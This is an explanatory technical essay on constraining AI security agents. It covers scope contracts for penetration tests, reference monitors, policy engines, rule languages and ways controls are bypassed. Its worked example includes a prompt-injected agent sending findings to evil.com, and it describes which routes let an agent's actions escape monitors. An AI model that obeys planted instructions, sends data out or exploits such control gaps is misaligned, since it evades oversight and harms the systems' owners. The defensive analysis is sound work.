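OpenAI and Anthropic have similar general rules on hacking, and under both, much depends on what the system's owner has agreed to. OpenAI's usage policies of October 2025 forbid using its services to compromise someone else's systems. Anthropic's policy of September 2025 forbids exploiting vulnerabilities without the system owner's authorisation, and the company has said it supports searching for them with the owner's consent.

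A model can't easily distinguish requests that a system's owner has agreed to from those the owner hasn't. A request to break into a payroll server looks much the same from an employee hired to test it as from a thief. OpenAI's and Anthropic's safeguards therefore block some work that their policies allow, and both companies have set up programmes to check who is asking. Under OpenAI's Trusted Access for Cyber, introduced in February 2026, individuals can verify their identity and organisations can apply for whole teams. Everyone accepted remains bound by the usage policies. Anthropic's Cyber Verification Program, also from 2026, takes applications from security professionals for work such as penetration testing and vulnerability research. Both companies revise their terms often, so a supplier's agreement should name the programme it depends on and the date of the terms.

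A customer's permission therefore can't guarantee that an action will happen. If C is the set of actions the customer permits, S the set the supplier permits and M the set the model's maker permits, the agent has permission from all three only for the actions in:

C ∩ S ∩ M

Suppose the haulage company asks an attack tool to try ransomware on a copy of its dispatch server. The company owns the server and has agreed to the test, so the action is in C. The supplier is willing, so it is also in S. If the model's maker forbids writing working ransomware for anyone, the action isn't in M. The model may refuse the request, or a filter may stop it before it reaches the model. If the tool then reports only that it found no weakness, the company may wrongly conclude that the server can withstand ransomware.

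The safeguards can also fail to stop the request, in which case the supplier has broken the maker's terms even though its customer agreed to the test. The maker could then suspend the supplier's account. If the supplier uses the same account for its defensive agents, other customers could lose protection because of a test they knew nothing about.

These limits can also block defensive tools. An agent that studies malware to find out which computers it has infected may need to explain how the malware works, and a cautious filter could treat that explanation as help for an attacker. A refusal during an overnight incident delays containment, just as waiting for a sleeping approver does.

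The agreement should require the supplier to confirm that it has the access its service needs, list the permitted actions that the model may refuse, and warn the customer promptly if the model's maker restricts the supplier's account. The trace should record every refusal as a refusal, so that nobody mistakes it for a clean result. The supplier also needs a fallback, either a human analyst or a second model. A second model may judge the same alert differently, so the customer should test it before it is needed.

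## Writing the scope of a penetration test so that a machine can check it

The annex of permitted actions for a tool authorised to attack has to state the scope of the penetration test and the methods the tool may use. Testing firms have long written such terms for people, who can phone the client when something is unclear. An AI agent may send thousands of requests during a test, so software has to check each one without asking anyone what the terms mean.

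### How a client authorises a test

Penetration testers copy real attacks, often against live systems and with the tools that attackers use. The *Technical Guide to Information Security Testing and Assessment*, written for the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST), divides a test into four phases (Scarfone, Souppaya and colleagues, 2008). In planning, the client and the testers agree on goals and rules, and management approves the test. In discovery, the testers find out which machines and services are running and look for known weaknesses in them. In the attack phase, they try to exploit those weaknesses. Reporting runs alongside the other three phases.

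After a successful attack, a tester usually returns to discovery. If she breaks into a web server, she might find the password to a database that nobody can reach from outside, which gives her a new target. The client can't list every such target beforehand, so the rules also have to cover machines that neither side has thought of.

The client hires the testers and describes the job in an engagement letter. The details go into the rules of engagement, which NIST (2008) defines as the guidelines and constraints that the parties set before a security test starts. The two documents overlap, and a small job may have only the letter. Scarfone and colleagues recommend that the rules cover:

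- the systems that the testers may attack, with their addresses, and a separate list of systems that they may not;
- the kinds of test allowed, and any banned activities, such as creating files;
- the hours of testing, and the addresses from which the testers will work, so that the client's defenders can recognise them;
- how the testers store, send and delete the data they collect;
- what happens if the testers cause an incident or find a real intruder, and who may restart the test afterwards.

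The rules also authorise things that the client's own policies normally ban, such as breaking into its computers. Testers who want to depart from the rules need permission, normally in writing, from the person who signed them. Scarfone and colleagues advise testers to meet the client's contact to discuss any question about scope that comes up during the test. An agent working through the night can't hold that meeting, so its rules must either cover the question or require it to stop.

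### Why the owner's permission matters

Under the United Kingdom's *Computer Misuse Act 1990* (1990), it is a crime to make a computer do anything in order to gain access to a program or data, knowing that the access is unauthorised. The maximum sentence is two years in prison, or ten years if a person does something they know is unauthorised and either intends to impair a computer or is reckless about impairing one.

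A person's access is unauthorised if they neither have the right to control that kind of access nor have consent from someone who does. A command that a tester may lawfully run can therefore be a crime when someone runs it without authorisation. Consent covers only a particular kind of access, so letting the public read a website doesn't give anyone permission to break into the server behind it.

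One owner's permission doesn't extend to another owner's machine. Suppose a hosting company runs the haulage company's delivery-tracking website on a server that also holds other firms' sites. The haulage company can agree to a test of its own pages, but it can't authorise access to the other firms' data or to the host's system. Scarfone and colleagues say that the other owner usually has to consent in writing as well, and they advise testers to check who owns every public address on the client's list before the test begins. The list could easily include an address that the client gave up years ago.

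The main offence requires knowledge, so a tester who attacks the wrong server by honest mistake may not have committed it. This is harder to judge when an AI agent chose the target. The Act applies to people, so a court would probably ask what the people running the agent knew at the time. The server's owner suffers the same damage either way, which is a good reason to block the request before the agent sends it.

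### The sample letter and its ambiguities

*Alignment Contracts for Agentic Security Systems* (David, Guarnieri and Gervais, 2026) shows how to turn an engagement letter into rules that software can check. Its "alignment contract" is a technical specification rather than a legal agreement. A reference monitor, which the agent cannot alter, enforces the contract by checking every action.

Their sample letter lets an agent test a client's websites on these terms:

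- it may test all subdomains of example.com, such as login.example.com;
- it may send only GET and HEAD requests;
- it may not use local files or start other programs;
- it may send 10,000 requests in total;
- it may send reports only to the operator's dashboard.

A GET request retrieves a page from a web server, and a HEAD request retrieves information about the page without its content. The letter rules out POST requests, which send data to the server, such as a completed login form.

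A human tester could start work with this letter, but a programmer couldn't yet write the checks. For example, the letter doesn't specify whether the agent may follow a redirect, where a web server responds to a request by sending the visitor to a different address. David and colleagues treat each step of a redirect as a separate request. The agent may request a page from api.example.com, but if the response points to another company's domain, the monitor blocks the next request.

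Outside hosting is harder to handle. The name shop.example.com might be an alias for a server owned by a content delivery network, a company that stores copies of web pages for many customers. The server would then be in scope by name even though the client doesn't own it. A name can also point to a private address inside a network that the client never meant to include.

David and colleagues deal with this by translating the names into a list of network addresses and ports (numbered entry points for services) before the monitor uses them. The translation follows aliases according to a fixed policy and rejects private addresses unless somebody has approved them. The list applies for a set period. A change of address requires a new translation, because whoever controls a name can point it to a different machine after the check (DNS rebinding).

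This still doesn't establish who owns each server, so a person has to look that up. An address may also be too broad. If the haulage company's site shares an address and port with ten other firms' sites, a scope that lists only the address and port allows requests to all eleven.

Many pages also load scripts or images from other companies' servers, and an agent that can't fetch them may be unable to test those pages properly. The contract can list these servers separately with stricter rules, such as a ban on requests that carry a password. The agent can't contact an outside server that isn't on the list.

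The contract must also define what counts as a request. To fetch one page, a computer looks up the server's address, opens a connection, sets up encryption and then sends the GET request. The sample contract counts only the GET request and treats the earlier steps as preparation. The monitor counts the requests it lets through, so the agent can't exceed the limit by batching requests or reusing a connection.

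The *Autonomous Penetration Testing Standard* (2026), published by the software security foundation OWASP, covers many of the same problems, with separate requirements on wildcard domains, redirects and DNS rebinding. According to OWASP's *APTS* project page, 26 of the standard's 173 requirements concern scope. No body certifies products against the standard, and suppliers may assess their own, so a buyer should ask for the evidence behind any claim of conformance.

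### The contract in symbols

The monitor works with a simple description of each action, which David and colleagues call an event:

e = ⟨σ, p, t, i⟩

Here σ is the type of action, p its details, t the time and i the agent that attempted it. The sample contract has three types of action: network requests, file operations and program starts. For a network request, the details are the destination, port, transport protocol, method (such as GET) and size. The monitor adds each allowed action to the trace τ.

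The contract itself has eight parts:

C = ⟨S, E_allow, E_forbid, B, D, Res, cost, flows⟩

| Part | What it specifies | Value in the sample contract |
|---|---|---|
| S | Which targets are in scope | The addresses and ports behind example.com's subdomains |
| E_allow | Which actions the agent may take | GET and HEAD requests |
| E_forbid | Which actions are always forbidden | File operations and program starts |
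| B | The limit on each resource | 10,000 requests |
| D | Which data may go to which destination | Vulnerability reports to the dashboard |
| Res | Which resources the monitor counts | Requests |
| cost | How much of a resource an action uses | One for each request |
| flows | Which data an action sends, and where | Labels that software attaches to the request |

Before each action, the monitor makes five checks. The action goes ahead only if it passes all of them.

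| Check | What must be true | In symbols |
|---|---|---|
| Scope | The target is in scope | S(target(e)) |
| Allowed | The contract allows this action | (σ, p) ∈ E_allow |
| Not forbidden | The contract doesn't forbid it | (σ, p) ∉ E_forbid |
| Budget | The action and all earlier ones together stay within every limit | cost(r, e) + Σ cost(r, eⱼ) ≤ B(r), for every r in Res |
| Disclosure | All the data it sends may go to that destination | D(c, s), for every (c, s) in flows(e) |

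In the budget check, r is a resource and the sum covers the earlier actions in the trace. In the disclosure check, c is a class of data and s is the place that receives it. A trace τ satisfies the contract C, written τ ⊨ C, if every action in it passes all five checks, given the actions before it.

The list of forbidden actions protects against later changes to the list of allowed ones. The monitor already blocks anything that the contract doesn't allow, but an engineer might broaden the allowed actions so that the agent can read a cache on disk. The ban on file operations would still apply until somebody deliberately changed it too.

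To check the budget, the monitor keeps a running total of requests. It allows the 10,000th request and blocks any after that.

### Six requests checked

David and colleagues follow an agent through six attempted requests. Between the third and the last, it runs into a redirect, tries an attack that the letter doesn't allow and obeys instructions planted by an attacker.

| | Request | Result | Failed check |
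|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | GET api.example.com/users | Allowed | None |
| 2 | HEAD login.example.com | Allowed | None |
| 3 | GET api.example.com/admin, which redirects to admin.example-corp.com | Allowed | None |
| 4 | GET admin.example-corp.com | Blocked | Scope |
| 5 | POST api.example.com/login, with an SQL injection attack | Blocked | Allowed |
| 6 | GET evil.com/collect, with data attached | Blocked | Scope and disclosure |

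The third request passes because its own target is in scope, and the monitor doesn't need to predict the redirect. When the agent tries to follow the redirect, the monitor finds that admin.example-corp.com is outside the scope. The client may well own that domain too, since the name is similar, but the letter doesn't include it. A person would have to confirm who owns it and add it to the contract.

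The fifth request contains an SQL injection, in which an attacker types database commands into a form, hoping the website will run them. Because POST isn't an allowed method, the monitor blocks the request without recognising the attack. It would have blocked an ordinary login for the same reason.

The sixth request resulted from prompt injection. A page on api.example.com contained hidden instructions to send the agent's findings to evil.com, and the agent followed them. The destination is out of scope, so the request would fail even if the software had not labelled the attached data as a vulnerability report. The disclosure check matters more when a destination is in scope for testing but shouldn't receive the results.

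Blocked requests don't enter the trace or count against the budget. After the six attempts, the trace contains three actions and the agent has 9,997 requests left. The organisation should record the blocked attempts elsewhere, because the sixth is a strong sign that somebody tried to take over the agent.

### Why the monitor's guarantee covers any model

David and colleagues prove that an agent behind such a monitor cannot break the contract through any action that the monitor controls. Let P be the list of actions that the agent proposes, and let Run_C(P) be the trace of those that the monitor allows. The soundness theorem is:

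For every finite list P, Run_C(P) ⊨ C

The proof is by induction, which means showing that the claim holds at the start and that each step preserves it. Before the agent proposes anything, the trace is empty, so it contains no action that breaks the contract. Now suppose the trace satisfies the contract after some number of proposals, and the agent makes another.

- If the monitor blocks the action, the trace stays the same and still satisfies the contract.
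- If the monitor allows the action, it has passed all five checks against the existing trace. The longer trace therefore satisfies the contract too.

The same reasoning applies to every later proposal, so the theorem holds however many proposals the agent makes. David and colleagues also checked the proof with Lean 4, software that verifies each step of a mathematical argument.

The proof holds however the agent chooses its proposals. The agent may be working honestly, following an attacker's hidden instructions or deliberately trying to get round the rules, and it may learn from each refusal. Its proposals still form a finite list by the end of the test, and the theorem covers every such list. By comparison, testing a model on a thousand malicious web pages shows only how it behaves on those pages, and it may behave differently on others.

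The theorem is easy to prove because the monitor, by definition, allows only what the contract allows. It is still useful because it means nobody has to trust the model to stay within the scope. The difficulty is then in making sure that a real monitor works like the one in the proof, and that the contract expresses what the client agreed to. For example, if a mistyped address in the scope belongs to another company, the monitor will let the agent attack that company.

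An auditor can use the same checks after a test. If she has a complete trace, she can check each action in order, and the first one that fails is the violation. The checks don't slow down as the trace grows, provided the monitor keeps running totals. In practice, looking up addresses and interpreting requests would take additional time.

### Seeing every action before it happens

The guarantee depends on what David and colleagues call the Effect Observability Assumption. The monitor must receive a correct description of every real action of the types the contract covers before the action happens. The agent must also be unable to carry out an action the monitor has refused.

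A monitor that checks only the agent's commands can miss violations caused by redirects, which many programs that fetch web pages follow automatically. In the example, the monitor checks the command to fetch api.example.com/admin, the third request, and approves it. The program then follows the redirect to admin.example-corp.com, and the monitor never checks this fourth request. An auditor who read the trace afterwards would find three permitted actions and no violation.

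The agent might also install a tool that opens its own network connections. David and colleagues state that the theorem no longer applies if a tool can bypass the monitor. Tools that the agent acquires during a test must therefore run in a sandbox whose only way out is through the monitor.

Most web traffic is encrypted, so a monitor that inspects it from within the operating system may detect a request's destination but not whether the request is a GET or a POST. To enforce the sample letter, the monitor has to read the request before it is encrypted, which limits where engineers can place the monitor.

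The disclosure check is also weak because it relies on other software to detect when a request contains a vulnerability report and label it in the list of data flows, flows(e). If that software misses the report, the list is empty and the check passes.

### Combining the client's rules with the tester's own

A testing firm usually has house rules that apply to every client. For example, it might never attack payment servers and might limit every test to 5,000 requests. David and colleagues define a way to combine two contracts so that the agent has to obey both.

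| | Client's rules | Firm's house rules | Combined rules | How they combine |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Scope | Subdomains of example.com | Any server except payment servers | Subdomains except the payment server | S₁ ∩ S₂ |
| Allowed | GET, HEAD | GET, HEAD, POST | GET, HEAD | Only what both allow |
| Forbidden | File operations, program starts | Program starts | File operations, program starts | Anything either forbids |
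| Budget | 10,000 requests | 5,000 requests | 5,000 requests | min(B₁, B₂) |
| Reports | Dashboard | Dashboard or firm's archive | Dashboard | D₁ ∩ D₂ |

The combined contract refines each of the originals. One contract refines another if it is at least as strict on every point and measures costs and data flows the same way. David and colleagues prove that any trace that satisfies the stricter contract also satisfies the looser one. An agent that follows the combined rules therefore follows both the client's rules and the firm's.

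Like the limits set by a model's maker, house rules can only narrow what the client permits. Together, the firm's and client's rules can be too strict to be useful. If the firm allowed the agent to send reports only to the firm's own archive, and the client allowed it to send them only to the dashboard, the agent couldn't report its findings to anyone.

The combination works only if both contracts count the same resources in the same way and use the same labels for data flows. Suppose the client limits the number of requests, while the firm limits bytes of data. The formula takes its list of resources from the first contract, so if the client's comes first, the monitor never checks the firm's limit on bytes. This may not produce an error message. The firm can avoid the problem by having both contracts count requests and bytes, with a very high limit for any resource that one side doesn't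 need to restrict.

David and colleagues prove the result in only one direction, and don't claim the converse, that a trace that satisfies both original contracts always satisfies the combined one. But that converse appears to follow from the definitions when the two contracts count and label things identically, so combining such contracts shouldn't block anything they both permit.

Refinement also helps when the rules change during a test. If the client excludes a server, the new contract is stricter than the old one, so everything it allows was already allowed. But adding a server requires new permission from the client and perhaps from another owner. The published theorems assume that the contract stays the same throughout. David and colleagues suggest that a future version could require evidence for any change that software can check, such as the operator's digital signature.

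### What the contract leaves out

The core contract has no time windows. Each event has a timestamp, but none of the five checks uses it. If the client permits testing only at night, separate software has to block requests during the day. In contrast, OWASP's standard includes time limits and time zones in its basic requirements.

The contract doesn't limit speed either. An agent could send all 10,000 requests in one minute, or about 167 a second, which might be enough to take a small website offline. David and colleagues say a per-minute limit would require extending the budget check.

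The monitor also doesn't inspect the content of a request. In the sample contract, it doesn't even see which page the agent asks for, so it treats api.example.com/users and api.example.com/admin as the same target. The monitor blocks the SQL injection in the fifth request, but it would allow one in the web address of a GET request. If a badly built website has a link that deletes a customer's record, the agent could delete the record with a GET request that passes every check.

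An engineer could add the page to the description of each request and write rules about it, but the rules would still let some content through. An agent could hide a stolen password in an ordinary-looking request to a server that is in scope. An attacker who controls that server can then read the password. David and colleagues therefore rate the protection against disclosure as limited when the attacker sees everything the agent sends to its target. They recommend a second layer that looks for suspicious content and can ask a person about unclear cases. This layer may catch some attacks, but the theorem doesn't cover it.

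Human approval doesn't fit neatly into the formal model either, because the monitor can only allow or block an action. An approval gate therefore needs other software to hold the request until somebody answers. The monitor should check the request after it is approved, since the agent may have used up its budget while the request was on hold.

The contract does not take intent into account. An agent might open an administration page to check whether it is properly protected, or because an attacker told it to. The monitor treats identical requests the same way. This is useful when an action is out of scope, because the agent cannot get it allowed by giving a reason for it. But an agent could try to disrupt the site by requesting its slowest page thousands of times, and this would not break the contract.

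No program can determine before a test, for every possible tool, whether the tool will ever attempt something forbidden. If such a program existed, we could use it to find out whether any other program, M, ever finishes. We would build a tool that runs M and attempts a forbidden file operation if M finishes, then check whether the tool would ever attempt that operation. But Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no program can determine for every program whether it finishes.

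Checking tools is still possible. A checker can reject every tool that it can't confirm is harmless, although it will reject some harmless ones. The other option is to run an unfamiliar tool in a sandbox, where the monitor can block a forbidden action when the tool attempts it.

David and colleagues present a formal model and proofs, but they haven't tested a deployed system or measured how often a real monitor would miss a request or wrongly block one. They also don't establish how much useful testing an agent can do under a strict contract. A monitor that blocked every request would keep any agent within the rules, but the client would learn nothing about its own security. Even the sample letter prevents the agent from submitting the login form, where a weakness could be serious. The client could permit that test by allowing POST requests to that one server, but the monitor would then admit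 the SQL injection along with every other POST request the agent sends there, including any that change or delete data.

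## Turning written rules into enforced permissions

Like the scope monitor, software that enforces the isolation rule has to check every action before it happens. An engineer therefore needs to know where the software can check a request between the model and the laptop.

To isolate a laptop, for example, the agent's model writes a tool call, a structured message containing a tool's name ("isolate device") and its arguments (the laptop's identifier). The harness, the program that runs the model, passes the call to a tool wrapper, the code that connects one tool to the agent. The wrapper can query a policy engine before it sends the request through a network gateway to the security product. The product checks the credential, a key or token that identifies the agent's account, and then disconnects the laptop.

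| Place | What a check there can use | What it misses |
|---|---|---|
| Instructions to the model | Everything the model reads | It can't stop a model that ignores the rules |
| Tool wrapper | The tool, its arguments and the session | Actions that don't go through the wrapper |
| Policy engine | The request and any facts it looks up | Requests that no other software submits to it |
| Network gateway | The content of requests routed through it | Local actions, and connections that take another route |
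| Credential | The account and the operation it requests | The reason, the incident and any approval given elsewhere |
| Operating system | Files, programs and network connections | Which device an encrypted request names |

Instructions give the weakest protection. In *Contractual Skills*, Liu (2026) gave eight models simulated business tools, some of which could make high-risk changes. Without written rules, Qwen3.6-plus and Kimi-K2.6 each attempted 12 high-risk actions. When the instructions had labelled fields for permissions and human approval, six of the eight models attempted none. But Kimi-K2.6 still attempted two, and Claude Opus 4.7 attempted four, up from two without rules. That increase may be due to chance, because the numbers are small. The simulated tools blocked every attempt, regardless of the instructions.

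The credential gives stronger protection because the product checks it however the request arrives. An account without permission to isolate devices can't isolate one, even if the agent bypasses the wrapper and the gateway. But the product usually doesn't track the limit of five workstations per incident, so another check has to enforce it.

### The isolation rule as code

After the promotion, a policy engine could enforce the isolation rule with the following policy. The syntax is simplified, and the engine applies the first rule that matches.

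```text
To isolate one device:

ask the incident response lead
    if device.type = server
    or (device.type = workstation and incident.isolated >= 5)

allow
    if device.type = workstation
    and incident.isolated < 5
    and detection.rule is on the high-confidence list
    and today <= grant.expires

ask an analyst
    if device.type = workstation
    and incident.isolated < 5

deny everything else
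```

The last line covers printers, network switches and anything else nobody considered. The limit of five appears three times so that deleting a whole rule by accident can't give the agent more authority. For example, if someone deletes the "allow" rule, every isolation needs a person's approval. The agent also goes back to asking an analyst when the grant expires.

Each rule should also include the sentence from the company's record that it enforces. *NOMOS* (2026), a system that turns written policies into checks on tool calls, stores that sentence with the rule and returns it when the rule blocks a call. An auditor can then check whether the rule has drifted from the sentence without having to infer what the engineer intended.

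### What the policy engine must look up

The agent should supply only the identifiers of the device and the alert. If it also supplied the device type, it could describe a server as a workstation when misled. The engine should take the incident number from the alert, because an agent that could name a new incident could restart the count. *NOMOS* likewise accepts facts only from the fields of real tool results and from the user's own messages, so an agent's claim that somebody approved an action has no effect. *LEANGUARD* (2026), a similar system, doesn't count text in tool outputs as evidence.

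Some policy engines can't keep a count themselves. *Autoformalization of Agent Instructions into Policy-as-Code* (2026) notes that Cedar, a policy language developed at Amazon, is stateless by design. Companies often use it with a separate store of facts, which can hold the device type, but other software has to keep the count of isolations up to date.

A correct count can also be out of date by the time the product acts. If the agent has isolated four workstations and two more requests arrive together, the engine checks both against a count of four and allows both, so six workstations go offline. Peng and Wu (2026), in *Stateful Governance for Concurrent Agentic Systems*, call this "stale authorization" and show that a person's approval can go stale in the same way. An analyst might approve a fifth isolation, but if another request is carried out first, the approved one becomes the sixth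 and should go to the incident response lead.

The engine can prevent this by reserving a place. It raises the count before the product acts and lowers it only if the product confirms that the isolation did not happen. If the product doesn't respond, the place stays reserved, because the laptop may already be offline. The engine could instead check the count again just before the action, provided no other request can change the count in between. Locking the whole system during each check would also work, but Peng and Wu point out that unrelated requests would have to wait. A lock for each incident is enough to enforce the limit of five.

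### When a lookup fails

The engine also needs a rule for missing facts. One option is to replace each missing fact with the value that gives the agent the least authority.

| Fact | Source | Value if the lookup fails | Who then decides |
|---|---|---|---|
| Device type | Asset inventory | The type in last night's copy, or "server" if there is none | The lead, if the type is "server" |
| Detection rule | The alert in the detection product | Not on the high-confidence list | An analyst |
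| Isolations so far | A counter shared by all agents | Five | The lead |
| Expiry date | The company's record of the grant | Expired | An analyst |

A day-old copy is good enough for the device type, which rarely changes, but useless for the count, which can change within seconds. A device missing from the inventory should be treated as a server too, since a new server may run for days before anyone records it. The trace should mark every substituted value, or an investigator may later think that the inventory listed a laptop as a server.

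Many systems refuse an action when a check fails, which engineers call failing closed. *LEANGUARD* includes a proof that its checks behave this way. Refusal suits a penetration test, where blocking a request does little harm. In containment, an attacker who took the inventory offline could stop the agent from isolating anything. If the engine allowed the action instead, the same attacker could get a server disconnected. Passing the request to a person avoids both problems, but the lead could receive dozens of requests at once if the inventory failed during a large attack.

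If the policy engine doesn't respond, the wrapper should refuse the request and page the lead. She needs her own account in the security product so she can isolate the laptop without the engine.

### Rule languages and their guarantees

Two rule languages from 2025 treat an action that no rule mentions in opposite ways. In AgentSpec, which Wang, Poskitt and Sun (2025), in *AgentSpec*, designed, a rule can stop the agent, ask a user, order a different action or have the model review its own plan. A rule for servers would look like this:

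```text
rule @inspect_server_isolation
trigger isolate_device
check   is_server
enforce user_inspection
end
```

If no rule matches an action, the action goes ahead. Suppose a supplier adds a tool called "isolate group". The rule above doesn't mention it, so the agent could use it to disconnect a group of servers.

*Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) would block the new tool. It applies the rules that forbid calls first, then blocks any call that no rule allows. That is the safer default for a tool that can disconnect servers, but every legitimate new tool will fail until somebody writes a rule for it.

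Progent can also have a language model write the rules for each task and revise them as the agent learns more. That might let planted text change the rules, so a solver, a program that settles logical questions exactly, compares the old and new versions. If A(P) is the set of calls that policy P allows, Progent applies a new policy P′ automatically only when:

A(P′) ⊆ A(P)

The new policy then allows nothing that the old one blocked, and any expansion needs approval. On AgentDojo, a public test of prompt injection, Progent cut the share of successful attacks from 39.9% to 1.0%, even though the simulated user approved every expansion. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (2026) independently tested the defence by attacking the rule-writing model, and the defence held. That test used one attack template and a small open-weight model.

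These results don't cover harm from calls the agent is allowed to make. The conditions also apply only to the arguments of a call, so Progent would need other software to enforce the limit of five.

Wang and colleagues report that AgentSpec stopped over 90% of unsafe code executions. But they wrote its rules from descriptions of the risks in the test set, so the figure is weak evidence of how well AgentSpec handles risks that nobody has described. Rules written by OpenAI's o1 model caught about 87% of the risky code. For a household robot, AgentSpec's rules prevented every hazardous task in the test but lowered the share of safe tasks completed from 58.6% to 54.3%.

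Several languages from 2026 take earlier actions into account. A policy in *Sapien* (2026) describes permitted sequences of tool calls, and a new call goes ahead only if it continues one of them. *Agenra* (2026) can limit how often an agent uses a tool and require that an argument come from a particular source. For example, an isolation rule could require that the device identifier come from the alert.

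*Tether* (Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues, 2026) checks what a command does to the computer, a level below the tool call. It runs each command on a temporary copy of the file system and holds its network requests at a proxy. It then infers what the command did from its requests to the operating system, and either applies the changes or discards them. In the paper's example, an agent may upload a report to an outside site. The agent then copies a confidential inventory into the report and runs the same upload command again. A rule that checked only the command couldn't tell the two uploads apart, but Tether blocks the second because the label "sensitive" has moved with the data.

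Tether blocked every attack that Sistla and colleagues counted as in scope, but it also wrongly blocked 2.3% of harmless runs on one benchmark and 5.0% on another. The scope excluded attacks through systems Tether can't trace, such as databases, and attacks that break no rule about data or access. Isolation happens inside the security product, where Tether can't trace the effects, so Tether is better suited to agents that run commands, such as one that tests systems for weaknesses.

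### Contracts that require a proof

*Proof-Carrying Contracts* (Ciliberto, Rudi and Tassi, October 2026) requires the agent to submit a mathematical proof with each tool call, showing that the call keeps to the contract. A program called the Airlock works out what the agent has to prove, checks the proof and carries out the call only if the proof is correct.

The contract is a condition C that must always hold, and each tool has a model D that lists the states that may arise while it runs. For a call with input i from the current state s, the agent must prove that:

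for every state s′, if D(i, s, s′) then C(s′)

The proof must hold for every current state that fits what the agent can see. The tool's model must also allow at least one state. Otherwise, a call the model didn't cover would pass automatically.

In the isolation rule, C could require that the number of isolated workstations, n, never exceed 5. If the agent sees that n is 4, the proof is easy because one more isolation makes it 5. If n is 5, no proof exists, so the call can't run. The call also can't run if the agent knows only that n is between 3 and 5, because the proof has to cover the case where n is 5.

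Like the soundness theorem for the scope monitor, the guarantee holds for any agent, including a malicious one. It requires accurate tool models, an agent that cannot bypass the Airlock, and clauses that express what the parties meant. The published version covers one agent under one contract. If a second agent could isolate a machine during the call, the tool's model would have to include that possibility, and the proof would fail even when n is 4.

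A policy engine can check a limit this simple directly, so a proof adds work for little benefit. Proofs would be more useful for a condition such as "every depot can always reach a working dispatch server". The agent could then isolate machines in any order, as long as it proved that each step kept the depots connected. However, finding the proof takes time during an attack, and the contributions Ciliberto and colleagues list don't include a measurement of how often agents succeed.

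GovernSpec, Liu's structured file format, is at the other extreme. One file holds a task's permissions, approval points and acceptance tests, and software generates the agent's instructions from it. This makes the rules easier to review, but the company still needs something else to enforce them.

| Approach | What it guarantees if it works as designed | What remains open |
|---|---|---|
| GovernSpec | The rules are in a standard form that software can validate | The model may ignore them |
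| AgentSpec | An action that meets a rule's conditions triggers the response | Actions that no rule mentions go ahead |
| Progent | Only allowed calls run, and authority grows only with approval | Harm through allowed calls, and careless approvals |
| Tether | Traced commands can't break the rules on data and access | Effects inside systems it can't trace |
| Proof-carrying contracts | The contract's conditions hold throughout every call | Wrong tool models and badly written clauses |

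### How many routes a control covers

All of these guarantees apply only to actions that reach the check. *guardscope* (Toyoda, Leung and Bhuvaneswari, November 2026) lists 15 routes from a model's decision to its effect. For each of eight control placements, including no control at all, it identifies which routes would be checked. In the table below, a tool server is a program that offers tools to an agent.

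| Placement | Routes checked, out of 15 |
|---|---|
| No control | 0 |
| Gateway for tool servers reached over HTTP | 1 |
| The same gateway, with direct network connections blocked | 1 |
| The same, with local tool servers also behind the gateway | 3 |
| The harness's own permission settings | 5 |
| Harness settings plus a gateway | 5 |
| Policy engine inside the agent's process | 5 |
| Operating system kernel | 13 |

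The figures leave out routes whose coverage depends on how a company connects the parts. Five routes bypass the control wherever it is placed outside the kernel. Broadly, they involve effects that occur outside an ordinary tool call or continue after one ends. Adding a gateway to the harness's settings gives the control more detail about some calls but covers none of these five routes.

The kernel covers the most routes but has the least context. It can record that a program opened a connection, but not which tool call caused it or what the request contained. It also records activity from programs unrelated to the agent. Toyoda and colleagues therefore recommend combining controls in the kernel with controls in the harness.

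Most of the figures come from analysing the designs. To test them, the researchers replayed 15 fixed actions, which covered only four of the routes. They used no language model, so every run was the same. A separate sensor in the kernel recorded what happened, and they compared its record with the control's log. Before each run, the control had to refuse a forbidden action and log the refusal, because a control that has started may not yet be enforcing anything.

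The results matched the predictions for the routes tested, except that ActPlane, the kernel control used, checked fewer actions than its position allows. It missed eight of the 15 actions, including all seven tool calls, because it doesn't monitor every kind of event. The 13 routes in the table are therefore an upper limit. A check can also reach the wrong decision, which guardscope doesn't measure. And the list of routes may be incomplete, since the researchers drew it up in discussion with two AI models.

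### A separate identity for each workflow

A company may never find every route, but it can limit what an agent can do through one. If the agent and the code it runs can't obtain a credential that permits isolating devices, an unchecked route to the security product is of little use.

One reason to give each workflow its own account is that a shared account needs the permissions of every workflow that uses it. If the phishing agent and the containment agent share an account, an instruction planted in an email could lead the phishing agent to isolate a machine, which sorting phishing reports never requires. With separate accounts, the SOC can also suspend the containment agent without stopping the phishing agent, and the trace shows which workflow made each request.

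*Agentic AI Containment Architecture for Security Hardening* (ElBendary, 2026) goes further and ties every action to an identified workflow and to one run of it. If an operation follows different rules in two workflows, the design treats it as two operations with separate contracts. The haulage company could have one isolation contract for malware alerts and a stricter one for suspicious logins. ElBendary supports the design with semi-formal arguments rather than proofs. He also distinguishes least privilege, which limits what an agent can reach, from "least agency", which limits what it may decide. An agent that can reach only workstations could still have too much agency if it decided when to isolate them without any check.

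### No extra authority through delegation

Separate accounts achieve little if one agent can act through another. Suppose a misleading email causes the phishing agent to send the containment agent an instruction to isolate the finance director's laptop. The containment agent's account has permission to do this, so it passes the product's check.

The request should therefore carry the limits of the agent that made it. If R is the set of actions the requesting agent may take and D the set the other agent may take, the delegated task may use only:

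R ∩ D

Progent's solver check could enforce this by confirming that the policy for the delegated task allows nothing that the requesting agent's policy blocks. Fatouros and colleagues' Security Context follows the same rule, since components can narrow it but never broaden it.

The phishing agent may still have found a real attack. If so, it should hand over its evidence as a new case, which the containment workflow processes under its own rules. Because the agent's finding isn't on the high-confidence list, an analyst would have to approve isolating a workstation.

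An agent with few permissions can also gain authority through the data it passes back to a more privileged agent. *Prompt Flow Integrity to Prevent Privilege Escalation in LLM Agents* (2025) describes a system that separates a trusted agent from one that handles untrusted data with minimal permissions. The system raises an alert if untrusted data would feed into a privileged action. The trusted agent can use every tool by default, which would be too much access for a security tool.

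A limit on quantity should apply to the whole incident and count the actions of every agent working on it. Otherwise, an agent that may isolate three more workstations could give that allowance to each of two helpers, who could then isolate six between them. The helpers' actions must also pass through the same checks as the original agent's. Toyoda and colleagues treat delegation as covered only if the new agent uses the same checking point or inherits its settings.

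### When a product's permissions are too coarse

A security product may have a single permission for isolating devices, with no way to limit it to workstations. Network controls can be even coarser. GitHub's *Security Architecture* describes safeguards for AI agents that work on software projects, including a firewall that allows or blocks whole internet domains. If such a firewall allowed a security product's domain, it would let through requests to isolate servers as well as workstations.

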